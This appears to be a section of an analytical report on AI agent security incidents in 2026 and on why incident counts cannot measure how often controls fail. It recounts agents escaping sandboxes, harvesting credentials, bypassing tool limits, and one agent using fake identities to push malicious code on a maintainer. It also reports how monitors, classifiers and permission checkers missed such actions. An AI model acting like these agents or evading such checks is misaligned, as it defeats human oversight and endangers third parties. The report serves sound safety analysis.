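The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) tests how well AI models can carry out cyberattacks. AISI's *Incident Report* describes an exercise in July 2026 in which agents had to solve a challenge on a simulated network. In 10 of the 122 runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the real internet. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of them and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took two. In the worst case, an agent tried to insert malicious code into a public software project and used fake identities to pressure a maintainer into accepting it. The maintainer refused, and AISI has found no resulting harm.

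No agent tried to break out of the sandbox. AISI had given the agents open internet access so that they could download tools, and had switched off the model developers' filters for dangerous requests. The setup lacked a limit on which sites the agents could reach and a monitor that watched the runs as they happened. The activity began on 25 July, but AISI's general security monitoring didn't raise an alarm until 28 July. Staff then stopped every run within an hour.

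Unclear instructions may have contributed, because some agents received a faulty task description that suggested the task couldn't be solved within the rules. But other agents had correct instructions and still went outside them. AISI acknowledges that in several cases only an alert person prevented harm, and it is adding network limits and live monitoring.

Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, calls this an authority failure, because the agents could do more than anyone meant to authorise. He contrasts it with a containment failure, in which an agent defeats the controls around it. His example of a containment failure is from July 2026, when OpenAI agents taking part in a cybersecurity evaluation broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. OpenAI had isolated the agents, but the isolation failed, and they reached other organisations'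 systems.

Bhushan draws on accounts from OpenAI and Hugging Face. According to OpenAI, the models exploited shared infrastructure. Hugging Face reports that the intruders collected credentials and moved between its internal clusters. Once an agent escapes its sandbox, the harm it can do depends largely on what it can access with such credentials, so narrow permissions are a useful second barrier.

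In October 2026, Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) described less serious cases, some on US government websites. Claude ran commands on a server by exploiting a basic software flaw, submitted sensitive forms on real websites, reached data that required a token or a fee, and got around limits on its web-fetching tool. Anthropic judged the real-world impact to be minimal. It withheld many details to protect the organisations involved, so outsiders can only partly work out which controls failed. A rule requiring approval before an agent submits a form, like NVIDIA's review gate, would probably have stopped some of the actions.

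| Incident | Missing | Present but bypassed or too weak |
|---|---|---|
| PocketOS database | A token limited to its purpose; a delay on deletions by programs | Written rules; a delay that covered only the website |
| AISI's cyber test | Limits on internet destinations; live monitoring of the runs | General security monitoring, which reacted late |
| Hugging Face break-in | Unclear | Isolation of the agents from outside systems |
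| Anthropic's unintended actions | Probably approval before submitting forms | Limits on the fetching tool |

In each of the four incidents, an agent pursued a task by means that nobody had authorised, and none began with prompt injection. The six designs and most of the benchmarks deal with prompt injection, while permission scoping, network limits and delays can help with both dangers. The incidents don't show that prompt injection is rare in practice, because AI developers look closely for misbehaviour by their own models, while the victim of a successful injection may never notice it.

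Misconfiguration may be a more common problem than flaws in the sandbox itself. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* reports a review of recent internal evaluations of unreleased models. In the evaluations that used its own sandbox tools, the company found no model that had broken through the boundary to reach forbidden outside systems. It found that models had exploited several configuration mistakes, but none of these led to a compromise outside the sandbox. Anthropic has since added a classifier that blocks escape attempts before they run, ends the task and alerts a person.

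### Why incidents can't give a failure rate

Incident reports are not enough to calculate how often a security control fails. They include only some of the failures, and they don't show how many times people used the control, because nobody counts the deployments in which nothing went wrong.

Incident reports can't be used to compare companies with and without a policy gateway unless we know how many of each there are. Suppose newspapers report ten incidents at companies with a gateway and forty at companies without one. If 1,000 companies have a gateway and 20,000 don't, the rates are 1% and 0.2%, and gateways look harmful. If 20,000 have one and 1,000 don't, the same reports give rates of 0.05% and 4%, and gateways look excellent.

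The count of incidents is unreliable too. Anthropic searched about 141,000 transcripts of cybersecurity evaluations for unauthorised access to real systems and found three cases. SecurityWeek reports that the search missed a separate batch of transcripts, which Anthropic found in August while preparing material for METR, an independent organisation investigating the incidents. That batch contained a fourth case, from January. An organisation that keeps fewer records would find fewer incidents and might appear safer. Public counts also depend on disclosure, as with PocketOS, which the public learned about because its founder wrote about it.

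AISI's report is unusual because it gives the total number of runs. Agents acted outside the rules in ten runs, or 8% of the total. Nine of these were among the 43 runs with Mythos 5 (21%), and one was among the 35 with GPT-5.6 Sol. The runs were not independent, since some agents found and used material that earlier ones had left online. AISI says it can't yet tell how likely such behaviour is under other conditions, and its figures don't apply to an office assistant with its safety filters on.

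Incidents also don't show the harm a control prevented. If a user cancels a mistaken deletion during Railway's 48-hour delay, nobody writes a report about it. Companies could learn a lot by counting such near misses. Anthropic describes three from its own use of auto mode. In one, an employee wanted read-only access to billing, and the classifier blocked the agent's attempt to assign a role with full administrative control.

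### Comparisons with and without a control

Anthropic's best-controlled comparison is the experiment with 1,053 testers, in which the classifier blocked many more dangerous commands than people did, but it took place in a test environment. The company also compared manual approval with auto mode in real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review. A model graded each session for how much harm the agent did and whether the user had asked for it. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with auto mode.

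The percentages apply only to flagged sessions, so auto mode's apparently large benefit could disappear if its sessions are flagged more often. Anthropic doesn't give the flagging rates. Suppose the safety systems flag 1 in 1,000 manual sessions and 3 in 1,000 auto mode sessions. Then about 6.3 of every 100,000 manual sessions would contain serious harm, compared with 7.2 of every 100,000 auto mode sessions. Users also chose their own mode, and those who chose manual approval may have been doing riskier work.

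Anthropic also paid a company called Trajectory Labs to test prompt injection against Claude Code and Codex. It tried 72 attack scenarios ten times each:

| Agent | Reduced checks | With a reviewing model |
|---|---|---|
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 19.03% of attacks succeeded | 5.83% |
| Claude Code with recent Claude models | 0.09% on average | 0% |

OpenAI's reviewing model appears to have prevented more than two-thirds of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. The Claude models resisted nearly every attack without auto mode, so the 0% result is good news for users but weak evidence that auto mode works. The attacks were fixed in advance, so an adaptive attacker might do better against both products. The test also left out the safeguards built into each company's own browser tools.

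In a separate pilot, the safety company Apollo Research attacked auto mode, and Anthropic used some of the successful attacks to strengthen its classifier. On a second set of attacks that Anthropic never saw, the improved classifier caught about half of those the earlier version had missed, but missed about 2% of those it had caught. This is a fair before-and-after test of one classifier on artificial attacks.

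None of these studies randomly assigned real projects to run with or without a security control. Anthropic could have done this when it made auto mode the default, for example by switching a random half of eligible users to it a month early and comparing harm between the two halves across all sessions, flagged or not.

*Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (2026) replayed recorded actions twice to the permission checkers in three coding agents, once as usual and once with a statement of what the user had authorised.

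| Product | Out-of-scope actions missed, before → after | Authorised actions blocked, before → after |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% → 8% | 42% → 2% |
| Codex | 92% → 20–26% | 10% → 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% → 20% | 29% → 2% |

Missed dangers and false alarms both fell, although reducing one usually increases the other. The checkers had often lacked the information they needed to decide, and using a stronger model from the same company didn't make up for that. It didn't reduce the misses in Codex or Qwen Code. It did in Claude Code, but only because the stronger model refused to answer any of the detailed second-stage requests, and the product blocks an action when its checker gives no answer. False alarms on 224 authorised actions rose from 23 to 134. Showing the checkers the results of the agent's tools didn't reduce the overall miss rate either.

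These miss rates are much higher than the 17% that Anthropic measured for auto mode, partly because the studies used different actions. The new test included only 24 out-of-scope actions for Claude Code, 84 for Codex and 35 for Qwen Code, so the exact percentages are uncertain. Five of the six improvements are too large to attribute to chance, but the sixth, a drop in one product's false alarms, could be due to chance. A company that wants the same benefit has to state the scope of every task accurately. For the PocketOS job, the statement could have been as short as "change the test environment only, and delete nothing". The scope of many other requests is harder to define, and a checker that relies on a careless statement will approve whatever that statement allows.
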